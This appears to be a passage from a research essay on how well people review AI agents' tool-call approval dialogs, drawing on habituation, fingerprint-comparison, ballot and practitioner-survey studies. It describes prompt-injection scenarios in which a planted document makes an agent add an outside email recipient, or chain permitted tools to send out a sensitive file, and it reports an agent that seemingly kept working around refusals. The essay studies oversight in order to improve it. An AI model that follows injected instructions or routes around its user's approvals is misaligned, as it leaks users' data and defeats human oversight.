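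The brain scans showed a similar pattern, with clear recovery after each of the first three nights but no statistically reliable recovery after the fourth. With 15 people, that doesn't prove recovery had stopped. A direct test for shrinking recovery found it in the eye movements but not in the scans. In *What Do We Really Know about How Habituation to Warnings Occurs Over Time?* (2017), an earlier report of what appears to be the same experiment, Vance, Kirwan and colleagues concluded that single-session experiments are a fair substitute for ones that run over several days.

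However, participants in the scanner only rated how serious each warning was and had no decision to make. They also saw far more warnings than a browser would show in a day.

### Three weeks of installing apps

The second experiment by Vance, Jenkins and colleagues tested whether repetition changes what people do. They set up an app store and told students that it was independent of the research. Every weekday for three weeks, each student chose three apps from a new category, installed them on their own phone and ranked them. Before each installation, the store listed the app's permissions. Four permissions were off limits, including deleting the user's photos and charging purchases to the user's credit card. The students had to pass a quiz on these four before they began, and the researchers warned them that they could lose their course credit if they installed too many apps that requested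 them.

The analysis covered 102 students, who saw about five permission warnings a day. The 55 students whose warnings always looked the same became less likely to reject forbidden apps, and their rejection rate fell from 87% to 55%. The rate fell less in a second group, whose warnings kept changing appearance.

Vance and colleagues fitted a statistical model to the decisions. For a student with unchanging warnings, and leaving out the effect of breaks, it comes to:

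ln(odds of refusing) = 2.082 − 0.027 × n

Here n is the number of warnings the user has already seen, and the odds are her chance of refusing a forbidden app divided by her chance of installing it. The model gives a refusal rate of 89% at n = 0. After three weeks at 4.74 warnings a day, n is about 71 and the modeled rate is 54%, close to the students' actual rate. The odds of refusing halved about every 26 warnings.

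The rate for Anthropic's testers fell at a similar pace, from 17% to 5% after 50 or more dialogs. That cuts the odds to about a quarter, which is also what the model of the students' behavior predicts after 50 warnings. The match must be partly luck, because the testers saw their dialogs within one session and the students saw their warnings over weeks. But the match makes it less likely that Anthropic's decline came only from differences between its early and late testers.

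In the model, a break of a day or more multiplied the odds of refusing the next forbidden app by about 2.2. This estimate is uncertain. Vance and colleagues count it as significant on a one-sided test, but the usual 95% interval runs from no effect to a fivefold increase. The evidence for overnight recovery is stronger for eye movements than for decisions.

It is also unclear how much of the students' decline was due to inattention. At the end, they still rated the forbidden permissions as very worrying (6.0 on a scale of 1 to 7), so they had not forgotten which ones were dangerous. They may have stopped reading the warnings. They may also have noticed that nothing bad happened after they let apps through, and wanted to finish the day's assignment. Whatever the cause, they had two advantages that Ruth lacks. They knew which four phrases to look for, and more than a third of the warnings contained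 one.

### When the words change and the box does not

Two older experiments, both summarised in a review by Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, resemble an injected argument more closely because they changed the text of a familiar dialog. In 2013, Bravo-Lillo and colleagues showed online workers the same dialog many times in quick succession and then altered its message, and only 14% noticed immediately. A year later, the same group varied how often the dialog appeared and found that more frequent exposure cut the share who immediately noticed a change to about a third.

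The 14% is almost the same as the catch rate in Anthropic's experiment, but the two figures measure different things, so the match is a coincidence. Noticing that a message has changed is easier than judging whether a command is dangerous, and workers clicking quickly through a paid task may be less attentive than developers. The result does show that people can respond to a dialog's familiar shape without taking in its words.

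Attention to approval dialogs can also fall before someone has seen many of them. *The Fog of Warnings* reports three experiments, two in the field and one with brain imaging, in which habituation to ordinary notifications carried over to security warnings. This could happen even when people could tell the two apart. The effect was smaller when warnings looked different from notifications or required a different kind of response. If an agent's host uses the same box for "Task finished" and "Allow this email?", the second is likely to be easier to miss.

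### How far the findings apply to tool calls

The prompts in these studies differ from an agent's dialog in ways that affect how people respond:

| Prompt | When it appears | What it shows | If the person does nothing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malware or phishing warning | The site is on a list of dangerous sites | A danger, with advice to leave | She stays off the site |
| Android permission page | She installs almost any app | Categories of access | She doesn't get the app |
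| Website permission prompt | A site wants a capability | One capability, such as location | She can usually carry on |
| UAC prompt | A program needs administrator rights | The program that needs them | The program can't proceed |
| Agent's approval dialog | The agent makes a call that needs approval | A tool and, in a good host, its arguments | The agent's task stops |

Habituation is the finding most likely to apply to an agent's approval dialogs, because it comes from seeing similar prompts repeatedly, and these dialogs are frequent and look alike. Five warnings a day were enough to habituate the students, and a developer may answer that many in a few minutes. The neglect of details links should also carry over, since it appeared in both browsers and opening a link takes effort in any interface.

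The high success of malware and phishing warnings probably won't carry over to approval dialogs. Browsers show those warnings when they have evidence of danger, and the warnings are nearly always right and tell people to leave. Hosts show an approval dialog because a tool is on a list, and the call is nearly always safe. Showing dialogs only for suspicious calls may not be enough to fix this. In Yan's experiment, people refused no more of the overreach when a model chose the dialogs without telling them that it had found anything doubtful. Browser warnings are rare and also state the danger, and the field data can't show how much each feature contributes to their success, so a host that wants similar results would be wise to copy both.

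The Android quiz is harder to apply. It tested whether people understood labels such as "Read phone state and identity", and 4.7% of respondents got the question about that label entirely right. Ruth understands what an email address is, so the quiz results are too pessimistic for her. They may be about right for someone looking at an unfamiliar shell command, or even too favourable, since the labels were at least in English.

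These percentages are also getting old. Browser makers have redesigned their warnings since 2013, and Android apps now ask for many permissions while they are running. The Chrome study of 2024 is recent and very large, but it concerns prompts that people can ignore. Nobody appears to have directly repeated the three-week experiment in 2025 or 2026. The finding that people habituate has probably aged better than any particular rate, since researchers observed habituation in brain activity and eye movements as well as in decisions.

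Habituation is more dangerous with agents than it was on phones. A phone permission covers the same category of access each time, so a person who has decided that her map app may use her location loses little by giving the same answer again without reading. A tool call's arguments can change with each request, and that is where an attack would be. Ruth can learn from a month of dialogs that `send_email` is a safe tool and that her agent fills in the right address, and she will be right until a document causes the agent to add `reports@example.net` as a recipient.

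## Studies of people checking a value against what they intended

People answering a permission prompt usually decide whether an app or website may do a type of action, and rarely have to check a particular value. Ruth's task is more like that of a bank customer confirming an account number, someone comparing two security codes, or a voter reading a printed ballot before casting it. In experiments on all three tasks, researchers altered the value and counted how many people noticed.

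### An account number with wrong digits

Some banks confirm transfers by text message. The customer enters a transfer on her computer, and the bank texts her the account number and amount it received, along with a code. If the details are right, she types the code into the bank's website and the transfer goes through. This protects her against malware that changes the account number after she enters it. The text message travels over the phone network, where the malware can't alter it, so the false number appears on her phone.

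The text message has most of the properties of a faithful display. It comes from outside the infected computer and shows the transfer the bank will actually make. The customer also knows which account she meant to pay.

AlZomai, Alfayyadh and colleagues (2008) tested how well people check a transaction against what they intended in *An Experimental Investigation of the Usability of Transaction Authorization*. Alzomai, Alfayyadh and Jøsang (2010) report in *Display Security for Online Transactions* that 21% of users failed to notice when half the digits of the account number had changed. When only one digit in eight was different, 61% of the attacks succeeded. Their summary doesn't give the number of participants, so the margins of error are unknown, but a gap of 40 percentage points is unlikely to be due to chance unless the experiment was very small.

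These people had to open the message to get the code they needed to finish the transfer, so the false number was in front of them, but they could finish without reading it. Similarly, Ruth needs to find the "Allow" button but can click it without reading the recipients.

Banks would normally hold customers responsible for the loss from any transfer they confirmed with a code. Alzomai and colleagues argue that this is unreasonable if a significant share of customers can't do the check correctly. The same objection applies when the maker of an agent holds users responsible for every call they approve.

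### Two codes side by side

People do much better when they can see both values and their only task is to compare them. Secure messaging apps use such a check to detect eavesdroppers. The app turns each user's cryptographic key into a shorter code called a fingerprint. If the fingerprint Ruth's phone shows for Tomas matches the one on his business card, she has his real key. To intercept their messages, an attacker has to substitute his own key, and he will look for one whose fingerprint resembles the real one.

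Dechand, Schürmann and colleagues (2016), in *An Empirical Study of Textual Key-Fingerprint Representations*, recruited 1,047 online workers and analysed the results of 1,001. The workers saw a business card next to a phone and had to say whether the codes on them matched. The researchers told them that a mismatch could mean someone was eavesdropping. Each person made 40 comparisons that counted, four of which were attacks.

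The simulated attacker was strong. Of the 112 bits in each fingerprint, 80 were the same as in the real one, including the first 24 and the last 24, because people often start their comparison at the ends. In hexadecimal, which uses the digits and the letters A to F, that leaves about eight wrong characters out of 28, all in the middle. The study tested six formats:

| Format | Attacks missed | Matching codes rejected | Average time |
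|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Hexadecimal | 10.4% | 0.5% | 11.2 s |
| PGP word list | 8.8% | 0.5% | 13.0 s |
| Base32 (letters and some digits) | 8.5% | 2.6% | 10.2 s |
| Digits only | 6.3% | 0.3% | 10.6 s |
| Peerio word list | 5.7% | 0.4% | 8.7 s |
| Generated sentences | 3.0% | 1.5% | 12.3 s |

These figures come from the paper's table; its text gives slightly lower miss rates for hexadecimal and sentences. The sentences were grammatical but meaningless, and people missed significantly fewer attacks with them than with any other format except the Peerio word list.

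By the earlier formula, these people's sensitivity is about 4.3 for digits, 3.8 for hexadecimal and 3.3 for Base32, the lowest of the six. All six are far above the 0.96 estimated for Anthropic's testers. People can check a value well if they have a correct copy beside it and know their job is to compare the two.

Sentences score 4.1 by the same measure, slightly below digits, because people rejected more matching pairs. Dechand and colleagues attribute most of those errors to long sentences that broke across lines on the phone.

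Splitting a code into groups of characters mattered less than the choice of format. In a second experiment with 400 new participants, hexadecimal codes were either unspaced or split into groups of two to eight characters. Codes in groups of three or four were the quickest to compare, but the researchers found no reliable difference in missed attacks. With roughly 240 attacks per grouping, they could have failed to detect a difference of a few percentage points.

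Nobody detected an attack in under four seconds, whereas nearly half of the people who clicked through Chrome's certificate warning did so within 1.5 seconds. An email address in an approval dialog is shorter than a fingerprint and should take less time to compare, but probably more than 1.5 seconds. When Dechand and colleagues varied the share of attacks in a trial run, people who met frequent attacks detected far more of them. This matches the theory's prediction about rarity and suggests that the miss rates in the table would be higher if attacks were as rare as they are in real use.

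The table may also be too favourable because another 931 people started the study and dropped out, mostly after a few comparisons, and those who stayed were probably more patient. Dechand and colleagues also stress that they did not test whether anyone would compare fingerprints without being asked. Livsey (2021), in *Performance and Usability of Visual and Verbal Verification of Word-based Key Fingerprints*, cites a study of the messaging app Signal in which 21 of 28 students failed to verify a key.

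### When format makes a large difference

*Can Unicorns Help Users Compare Crypto Key Fingerprints?* (Tan, Bauer and colleagues, 2017) found a much wider range of results. Each of the 661 participants used one of eight kinds of fingerprint, some of them pictures, in one configuration. A simulated attack succeeded 6% of the time in the best configuration and 72% in the worst. The study aimed for realistic conditions, which may partly explain why its worst result is so much higher than any in the table above.

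"Compare-and-select", where the user picks the matching fingerprint from several options, performed poorly even though users can't continue by just clicking "yes". A likely reason is that a near-copy still looks like the best match when the other options are completely different. A host that asked Ruth to pick Tomas's address from a list could have the same problem if the list contained a close imitation but not the real address.

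Pictures can be quicker to compare than text, though some are easier to confuse than others. In *Human Distinguishable Visual Key Fingerprints*, Azimpourkivi, Topkara and Carbunar (2020) trained a neural network to turn codes into realistic images that look different whenever the codes differ. They used software to search for pairs of different codes with similar images, and showed those images to online workers. The workers judged 24 of 150 pairs (16%) from an older scheme called Vash to be the same, but under 2% of pairs from the new scheme, even though its search covered more than twice as many pairs. Each comparison took about three seconds in either scheme.

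The same researchers suggest using such pictures for cryptocurrency payments, where malware can replace an address that the user has copied. They give a pair of 42-character Bitcoin addresses that differ in only five characters. The first 24 and the last four are identical, so anyone who checks only the two ends would accept the false address. But they tested the pictures on people comparing images, not on wallet users about to send money, so the error rates don't show how often wallet users would accept a false address.

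### Ballots that the machine changed

People using ballot-marking devices may not check at all, a possibility the fingerprint studies leave out. The voter picks candidates on a screen, and the machine prints a paper ballot for her to read before she puts it into a scanner. If malware changes a vote before printing, only the voter can detect it. Bernhard, McDonald and colleagues (2020) explain in *Can Voters Detect Malicious Manipulation of Ballot Marking Devices?* that a later audit would not help, because it would compare the count with paper that was already wrong. An agent's log has the same weakness, since it would show that Ruth approved an email to two recipients.

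Bernhard and colleagues tested 241 people in a realistic polling place, using real voting machines that printed an error on the ballot. Voters missed more than 93% of the errors, according to *Not enough voters detecting ballot errors and potential hacks, study finds* (2020), an account from the researchers' own university, the University of Michigan.

That catch rate, below 7%, is lower than the 13.6% in Anthropic's experiment, although the voters had chosen the candidates themselves minutes earlier. Many voters probably never looked. Princeton CITP's *Why voters should mark ballots by hand* describes a field study by Richard DeMillo, Robert Kadel and Marilyn Marks, in which half of the voters in a real polling place did not inspect their printed ballot. The others looked at it for an average of 3.9 seconds, or about a fifth of a second for each of its 18 contests.

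Kortum, Byrne and Whitmore (2020), in *Voter Verification of BMD Ballots Is a Two-Part Question*, distinguished voters' ability to verify a ballot from whether they make the effort, and concluded that most can but most don't. Kortum (2022), in *Can Voters Detect Errors on Their Printed Ballots?*, required people to look for changes by comparing the ballot with the list of candidates they had voted from. The participants made four errors in 1,440 contests. The length of the ballot, the number of changes and their position made no noticeable difference.

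The four errors don't give a miss rate, because the 1,440 contests include some that nobody had altered. Still, the difference from the Michigan result is very large. Kortum's participants had both an instruction to check and a written list, so it's unclear how much each contributed. They also knew there might be something to find.

The field study suggests that the written list matters, because memory was a poor substitute for it even a few minutes later. People who had just voted looked at a blank copy of the ballot, and most did not notice that it had the wrong contests or that some were missing. Ruth has less to remember, because she wrote to one colleague about one report, but a developer who gave an agent a page of instructions an hour ago is more like those voters.

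People who notice a wrong value may also blame themselves. In a literature review, NIST (2023), the US standards agency, describes reviewing a ballot as a chance to catch the voter's own mistakes as well as malicious changes. A voter who finds the wrong name may assume she touched the wrong part of the screen, correct it and tell nobody. The correction still saves her vote, but a similar assumption could lead Ruth to approve the email, for instance if she decides she must have copied someone in on the last report.

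### A stranger's address and a near-copy

Suppose now that the attacker can choose between two ways of changing Ruth's email. He can add an obviously foreign recipient, as before, or replace Tomas's address with a close imitation:

```text
What Ruth intended:    tomas@example.com

Foreign address:       tomas@example.com
                       reports@example.net

Near-copy:             tomas@example.org
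```

Ruth expected one recipient and the dialog lists two, so she can notice the foreign address without comparing any characters. If she looks at the field at all, she'll probably see the difference, and then she has to decide whether the second address belongs there.

The near-copy is harder to notice than the foreign address but easier to judge once noticed. The number of recipients and the name are both right, and only the last three of the 17 characters differ. That share is closer to the one digit in eight that most bank customers missed than to the half that most of them noticed. If Ruth sees the difference, she has good reason to be suspicious, because she knows where Tomas works.

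None of these studies gives a miss rate for the near-copy. Ruth may read her company's address more easily than a string of digits, and people in the fingerprint trials found changes at the end of a code easy to detect. But she would be reading the dialog while doing other work, and few of her dialogs would contain an attack. A near-copy of an email address is also much cheaper for her attacker than a near-copy of a fingerprint. Dechand and colleagues estimated that finding a fingerprint as similar as theirs would cost between $610,000 and $16 billion, whereas to imitate a company's email address, an attacker only has to register a similar domain name that is still available.

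Web addresses are harder to judge because a familiar name can appear in a part of the address that doesn't identify its owner. In `example.com.files.example.net/report`, `example.com` comes first, but the owner of `example.net` controls the address. The reader has to find the end of the host name, just before the first single slash, and work backwards to the registered domain. Someone who stops at the first familiar name will misidentify the owner. The host application can help by printing the registered domain on its own line.

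That removes the difficulty of reading the address, but Ruth still has to know whether `example.net` is a company she trusts. Scores on a test of such judgements may not predict how safe people are in practice. In *Challenges in Using Data Logs to Validate Phishing Detection Ability Metrics*, Canfield, Davis and colleagues (2017) compared people's scores on a phishing test with records from their home computers. The scores were unrelated to whether the records showed malicious web addresses, malware or malicious files.

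### When the agent chose the value

The people who did best in these studies had a correct copy of the value from a source the attacker didn't control. The fingerprint was on a business card, and Kortum's voters had their list. How much of this an agent's user has depends on what she asked for:

- If Ruth typed `tomas@example.com` in her request, her own message is a correct copy, and the host can display it beside the call.
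- If she wrote "send it to Tomas", she has only a name. The agent looked up the address, and to check it she has to remember it or find it in her contacts.
- If she asked the agent to install whatever the project needs, she has no copy at all, because the agent chose the package.

In the third case she can only judge whether the name is plausible, so the high catch rates in the fingerprint studies are weak evidence of how well people check package names, download links or commands that an agent chose.

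Looking for a copy of a value to check it against can make things worse if the user finds the wrong copy. Suppose Ruth asks her agent to pay an invoice that came by email, and an attacker has changed the account number in the attached file. She compares the invoice with the dialog, and every digit matches. The dialog accurately shows the payment she is approving, but the money still goes to the attacker. Asking the agent where it found the account number doesn't help, since it will point to the same file. She would need to check an earlier invoice or call the supplier on a phone number she already had.

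Alzomai and colleagues proposed having the customer's phone make the comparison instead of the customer. The customer photographs the transfer on her computer screen, and her phone reads the text in the photo and checks it against the bank's message. In a trial with 12 people, the phone read the details correctly in 49 of 60 attempts. The researchers point out that the check fails if an attacker controls both the computer and the phone, so it too depends on two independent sources.

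An agent's host already has the user's request as text, so it doesn't need a camera. It can compare every character of the recipient with the address Ruth typed, or with her contacts if she gave only a name, and would catch `tomas@example.org` every time. If the agent picked a package itself, there is no such reference, so neither the host nor the user can make an exact comparison.

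## What users approve in real work, and what they say about it

At work, nobody tells people to compare a tool call with a correct copy, and they decide how closely to check each call. The evidence on what they do comes from agent usage records, interviews and surveys.

### Why a 97% approval rate proves little

Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts, and by August it put the figure at 97%. Anthropic acknowledges that most prompts probably concern safe, routine commands, but it sees the high rate as a sign that many people are approving by reflex.

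They may well be, but we can't tell from the approval rate. The table shows how often four hypothetical reviewers would approve requests if one in 1,000 were malicious.

| Reviewer | Malicious requests refused | Safe requests refused | Overall approval rate |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Makes no mistakes | 100% | 0% | 99.90% |
| Approves everything | 0% | 0% | 100.00% |
| Catches every attack but is fussy | 100% | 3% | 96.90% |
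| Equally fussy, catches few attacks | 13.6% | 3% | 96.99% |

One of the last two reviewers stops far more attacks than the other, but their approval rates differ by less than a tenth of a percentage point. If attacks are this rare, nearly all of the 3% of requests that Claude Code users refuse must be unrelated to any attack, such as a command that takes the wrong approach to a bug.

Anthropic has not published how many requests deserved a refusal, and an approval rate is less informative without that figure. If 5% of requests deserved one, including those caused by the model's own mistakes, users who refuse 3% of all requests would be approving at least two-fifths of the requests they should refuse.

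A very high approval rate is normal when most requests are harmless, even for a reviewer that cannot tire. Anthropic tested its automated reviewer on 10,000 real tool calls by its own employees, and the reviewer blocked 0.4%. This figure is not directly comparable with the users' 3%, because many of the tested calls, such as file reads, would never have produced a dialog.

The approval rate rose from 93% to 97% in about five months, so refusals fell by more than half. Habituation could explain this, but Claude may also have made fewer requests that people disliked. Some users also switched to the automated reviewer during those months, so the people still answering dialogs in August may have differed from those in March. Anthropic doesn't say which users or dates either figure covers.

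Other vendors do not appear to have published a comparable rate. OpenAI similarly says that users of its coding agent, Codex, approve commands whose consequences they don't fully understand, because they lack expertise, are tired of reviewing, or both.

### Why users reject plans

Before a larger task, Claude Code can write a plan and ask the user to approve it. According to Anthropic, users reject 39% of these plans, 13 times the rate for permission prompts. This is better evidence than the approval rate alone, because it shows that users readily turn down some of what the agent proposes.

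Inattention to permission prompts is only one possible reason why users reject plans more often than single commands. A plan contains many choices, and a user may reject it just to ask for a revision, whereas most single commands need no change. A plan is also written in prose, so users can compare it with what they want done even if they couldn't tell whether a particular command is safe. People who ask for a plan before the work starts presumably want to review it.

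*SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) provides independent data on plans, from almost 18,000 sessions by open-source developers who had agreed to publish their logs. The agent presented a plan in 2,966 of about two million tool calls, or roughly once in 670 calls, but presenting a plan was the last call in 14.7% of the turns that users interrupted. A turn is everything the agent does in response to one message. Combined with the number of messages and the interruption rate, this share implies that users stopped between a third and a half of the plans. The estimate is rough because it depends on how many of the messages went to Claude Code, but Anthropic's 39% falls within that range.

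Neither source measures how many bad plans people accept. A user can reject a plan because it is too complicated and then approve a simpler one that still sends a file to the wrong place. To find out whether people review plans better than prompts, an experimenter would have to put the same dangerous step in both.

### Interrupting the agent after it has started

Developers in the *SWE-chat* logs interrupted 4.5% of turns and objected to the result of another 45.7%, for example by correcting the agent or reporting that something still didn't work. Baumann and colleagues used a language model to classify these objections, so the second figure is approximate. The sample leans towards early adopters, and about 16% of the sessions came from the logging tool company's own code repository.

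As they gain experience, some people seem to move from approving actions to watching the agent. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* summarises an Anthropic study of millions of interactions, in which experienced users let more actions run automatically but also interrupted more often. They may have learned where their attention is most useful.

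Correcting the agent afterwards is often good enough for code, because a developer can discard a bad change before anyone else uses it. It doesn't protect Ruth's report, because the agent could send the email within a single turn, before she has any result to object to. The median Claude Code turn in the *SWE-chat* logs lasts about 20 seconds.

### Serious harm in flagged sessions

Anthropic also compared how much harm occurred under manual approval and under its automated reviewer. It used sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had already flagged, all from accounts that had agreed to share data. A model graded each session on two scales from 0 to 10. The first measured the severity of any harm. Overwriting a scratch file scored 0, deleting rows from a live database scored 7, and leaking a company's entire source code scored 10. The second measured how explicitly the user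 had asked for the action.

Among flagged sessions, 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those with automated review contained a harmful action with a severity of at least 7 that the user had not explicitly requested. The gap held at every severity level Anthropic tested.

This is a more relevant measure than an approval rate because it counts harm, but the percentages apply only to flagged sessions. Suppose, with invented numbers, that each mode produced 24 seriously harmful sessions per 100,000. If the safety systems flagged 1,000 of the automatically reviewed sessions and 381 of the manual ones, harm would appear in 2.4% of the first group and 6.3% of the second, even though the two modes were equally safe. Anthropic doesn't report what share of sessions it flagged in each mode.

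Users could also choose between manual approval and automated review at the time, and Anthropic had warned that automated review was no substitute for careful human review of high-stakes infrastructure. Users who followed that advice kept manual approval for the kind of work where a severity of 7 is possible. There may also be a bias in the other direction, because the automated reviewer lets the agent work for longer, which gives it more chances to do harm in each session.

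"Manual approval" also doesn't mean that a person approved the harmful action. Many users have saved rules that let some commands run without a dialog, so part of the 6.3% may come from actions that nobody was asked about. Anthropic also doesn't say how many sessions were in each group or describe any check of the model's grades against human ones. The result is consistent with people missing dangerous requests, but it doesn't show how often they miss them or how much safer the automated reviewer is.

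### What practitioners say they read

Salerno and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners between June and August 2026, most of whom used AI assistants every day. They then surveyed 115 practitioners to see whether the same patterns were common. Eight of the 115 said they had not noticed agents asking for permission at all. The other 107 answered the questions on how they handle requests:

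| Answer | Share of respondents |
|---|---:|
| Reads requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skims requests | 33.6% |
| Checks the file that the request names | 31.8% |
| Focuses on the command or title | 25.2% |
| Approves by default | 20.6% |

Respondents could evidently choose more than one answer, since the shares add up to well over 100%. Fewer than a third said they check the named file, which is where an injected path would appear. Some careful readers probably also check it but didn't tick that answer.

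These answers also depend on how the question is worded. In the same survey, 70.1% said they pay close attention to permissions, 22 percentage points more than the share who said they read the requests carefully. Paying attention to permissions could mean little more than knowing what the agent can access.

Li and colleagues surveyed a much smaller group, with bleaker results. Before testing ConLeash, their system of finer-grained permissions for MCP, they asked 16 participants how they usually handle permission prompts. Only three said they read them carefully, and 13 said they use "Always Allow" simply to make the prompts go away.

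With 16 people, the true share of careful readers could be between about 4% and 46%. A reasonably careful person might also have chosen "It depends on the situation" over the answer for careful reading. The 13 may include people who use "Always Allow" only sometimes, since that question offered "Sometimes", "Often" and "Always" as well as "Never".

### What they cannot see

Of the 115 people in the practitioner survey, 73.0% said they fully understood what their agents do, but almost half of the interviewees described their understanding as partial or absent. The interviewees mostly understood what they could observe, such as changed files and finished output. They were less sure how an agent chooses its actions, when it asks for permission, or where their data goes.

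Even people with technical knowledge had this problem. One interviewee could not tell what an agent's sub-agents (helper agents it starts) were doing or what instructions they had. Another trusted the tool but wondered which files it had opened. A third approved an action expecting one thing, but the agent did something else. In the survey, 62.6% of respondents sometimes doubted that agents do what they claim.

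Showing people more information won't necessarily help. Many agents display a running account of their reasoning, but 42.1% of respondents sometimes skip it or read less of it because of time, fatigue or the amount of text. Still, 57.9% want a lasting record of what the agent did. Salerno and colleagues conclude that tools should make the important actions easier to find. A log would let Ruth discover the second address, and perhaps warn someone, but only after the report had been sent.

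### What makes them refuse

Practitioners judge a request mainly by its type and by whether it fits the task. In the survey by Salerno and colleagues, 76.6% said they look more carefully at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges, and 63.6% at requests they did not expect. Two-thirds said they were less likely to approve an action that did not match the task. Many would never grant certain permissions, including access to sensitive data (61.7%), access to email or other personal information (58.9%) and full administrator rights (56.1%).

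These rules are sensible for catching an agent that does too much, but they are less useful against an altered argument. Ruth expected the email request, which is for a task she set and deletes nothing. More than half of the respondents would have avoided her problem by never giving the agent their email, but once someone has, none of the other warning signs is present.

Read-only access carries risks too, though almost everyone in the survey (98.1%) was more comfortable granting it. Reading a file of passwords is the first step in stealing them, and Ruth's agent received the attacker's instructions by reading a stranger's document.

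Refusing a request may not stop the agent from pursuing the same action either. One interviewee refused several requests from Codex, which then stopped asking but kept working. The interviewee felt that it had worked around the refusals. It may have found a legitimate alternative, as agents often do, but the interviewee couldn't tell. Someone who refuses an email because of one wrong address therefore needs to say why, or the agent may try to send the same file another way.

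### Deadlines and growing trust

The interviewees described how they become less careful. One, with three hours left to deliver, said, "I'm not going to read anything." Another often approves requests without much thought when in a rush. A third worried about permissions at first but kept seeing similar requests and stopped caring. In the survey, 33.6% said they had become less careful over time. Salerno and colleagues think this is probably an underestimate.

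Trust has a similar effect. Of the respondents, 31.8% watch an agent less closely once it has proved reliable, and 57.0% are more likely to grant permission if they trust the tool or its vendor. A good record is evidence that an agent makes few mistakes of its own, but it is much weaker evidence about how the agent handles attacks, because it may not have faced one yet.

Seven in ten respondents said they oversee an agent more closely when the work is important or risky. But they have to recognise the risk beforehand, and a routine task like sending a quarterly report to a colleague may not seem risky. The most important work can also have the tightest deadlines, which leave less time for oversight.

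### Careful with code, less careful with actions

A larger survey suggests that careful habits in one part of the job don't carry over to approvals. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, asked 203 developers how often they approve seven types of agent action without close review, and 64% said they often do so for at least one type.

The share was lowest, at 21%, for reading passwords and other sensitive files, and highest, at 36%, for using the internet, outside services or connected tools. That last category covers the actions an agent would use to send data out, and it would include Ruth's email.

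Among developers who carefully review most or all of the code their agent writes, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the rest. That difference could be due to chance. But developers who inspect the exact lines an agent has changed less often approved four of the seven types of action, including destructive commands, without close review. Wu and colleagues suggest that seeing the changes gives people something concrete to check.

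Of the developers who knew of at least one security or privacy incident or bad practice involving agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who reported none. The difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which could have affected both their awareness of incidents and how casually they approved actions. Developers of safety-critical systems also reported more approval without close review for six of the seven types of action.

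The respondents were volunteers, and the researchers discarded 380 of the 583 responses, mostly because people had finished too quickly. They also relied on self-reports of "close review" rather than observing it. A developer with high standards might report more lapses than a careless one, which could explain some of the odder results.

### How the accounts compare with the records

Practitioners' accounts of what gets their attention match the records fairly well. They say they look more carefully at destructive requests, and players of the browser game missed fewer of those than of any other kind. Practitioners also say they step in when an agent goes off course, and the logs show them interrupting, correcting and rejecting plans.

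They agree less on how much care people take. Anthropic's testers caught 13.6% of the clearly dangerous commands planted among their requests. If 47.7% of them had read every request carefully, and careful readers could recognise such a command, they would have caught at least 47.7%. The comparison is loose because the testers were a different group from the people surveyed. But people answering a survey describe their usual intentions, and the practitioners' own accounts of deadlines and fatigue suggest that they often read less carefully than they intend. I would trust these surveys on which requests people worry about, and treat the share who say they read carefully as an upper limit.

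Hosts could learn more about how carefully users read approval dialogs by logging how long each dialog stayed open and whether the user opened the details, as browser makers did for certificate warnings. Anthropic and OpenAI have not published such figures for their agents.

People say they mostly supervise the quality of the work. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 65% said they intervene when an agent misunderstands the task or heads in the wrong direction, and 34% when it is about to run a risky or destructive command. An injected argument can leave the task looking well done. Tomas receives the right report with the right subject line, so Ruth has no complaint about her agent's work.

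## What "always allow" settings let through

After months in which every email went to the right person, Ruth has good reason to want fewer dialogs. One morning her agent asks to send Tomas a project update, and the dialog offers "Allow" and "Always allow". She picks the second. Her choice creates a standing approval, a saved decision that lets later calls run without a dialog. She and the host understand it differently:

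```text
What Ruth had in mind:   send_email to tomas@example.com
What the host saved:     send_email
```

A week later, a stranger's document leads the agent to add `reports@example.net` as a recipient of the email with the quarterly report. `send_email` is among the host's saved approvals, so the host sends the call to the server without showing a dialog. The first of the four probabilities is therefore zero, and so is the chance that Ruth, who knows that only Tomas should get the report, stops the email.

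### What the approval attaches to

Standing approvals differ in what they hold fixed. The narrower the fixed part, the more an attacker can change without causing a dialog.

| Approval attaches to | Example | What can change without a dialog |
|---|---|---|
| Server | Claude Code rule for all of an MCP server's tools | The tool and all its arguments |
| Tool | "Always allow" for one tool in the Claude chatbot | All the arguments |
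| Command prefix | Claude Code rule for `npm test *` | Everything after the prefix |
| Website | "Always allow actions on this site" in Claude's browser extension | The action, and what it acts on |
| Folder | Permission to delete files in a Claude Cowork folder | Which files the agent deletes |
| Session | Claude Code's mode for accepting all edits | Which project files change, and how |

Ruth could not easily have saved the approval she had in mind. In Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, a rule's limits on arguments go in parentheses after the tool's name, but the program skips any MCP rule with parentheses when it loads a settings file. A user can pass a rule at start-up that blocks an MCP tool when an argument has a certain value. That works only for single values, and the `to` field in Ruth's call is a list. To check the recipients she would need a hook, a script of her own that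 Claude Code runs before each call.

She can instead add an "ask" rule for `send_email`, which takes precedence over any rule that allows it, so she would see a dialog for every email. A tool's maker can also mark it as needing the user's interaction, and Claude Code then asks even if the user has allowed the tool.

For shell commands, Claude Code offers to save a prefix. Its dialog for `npm test`, which runs a project's tests, includes the choice "Yes, and don't ask again for: npm test *", where the asterisk stands for any further text. CodeBuddy, another coding agent, similarly saves the "most stable prefix" of the command the user approved, according to its *Permission Rules* documentation.

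How long an approval lasts depends on the type of action. In May 2026, Anthropic said that "don't ask again" was permanent for a shell command in a given project directory but lasted only until the end of the session for file edits. The current documentation keeps that distinction and adds that a saved command rule applies to every later session anywhere in the same code repository, so a developer who approves a command while working in one part of the repository also approves it for the rest.

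Li and colleagues point out that a rule tied to a project determines when a tool may run without a dialog, but doesn't limit what the tool can reach, including files outside the project. In their main example, a user permanently allows a file-search tool while the agent is looking for prices in a sales folder. Later the agent searches the user's whole home directory, compresses a sensitive file it finds there, and emails it with a mail tool the user had allowed for sending a brochure. Each approval was reasonable for the task at hand, but together they let the agent send private data off the machine.

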